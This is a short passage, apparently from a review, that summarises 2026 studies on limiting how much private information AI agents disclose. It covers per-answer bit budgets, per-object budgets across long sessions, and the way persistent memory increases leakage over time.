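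Another remedy is a budget for how much the agent can reveal. *Answer-Only Disclosure* (2026) describes a ledger that measures the private information in each answer. In one test, the system revealed a planted code in 46 of 48 cases without a budget and in none with a budget of about 23 bits. The budget doesn't guarantee that the code stays secret, because the code had a million possible values and needed only about 20 bits, less than the budget. The median answer used about 14 bits, so two answers of that size could together carry the whole code.

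Budgets become more restrictive as an agent keeps working. *PlanTwin* (2026) gives each private object, such as a file, a budget that limits how much a cloud model can learn about it. Over a session of 58 tasks, the average planning score barely changed, from 0.773 to 0.767, but the score for coding fell from 0.753 to 0.520. Several of the coding tasks used the same objects, so those objects' budgets ran out and the system began to withhold information.

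Persistent memory can make accumulation worse. *Disclosure Begets Disclosure* (2026) simulated 300 people over 80 sessions each. In the later sessions, every model leaked more with memory than without it, although memory sometimes reduced leaks early on. Filtering reduced leaks but also made the models' help less useful.
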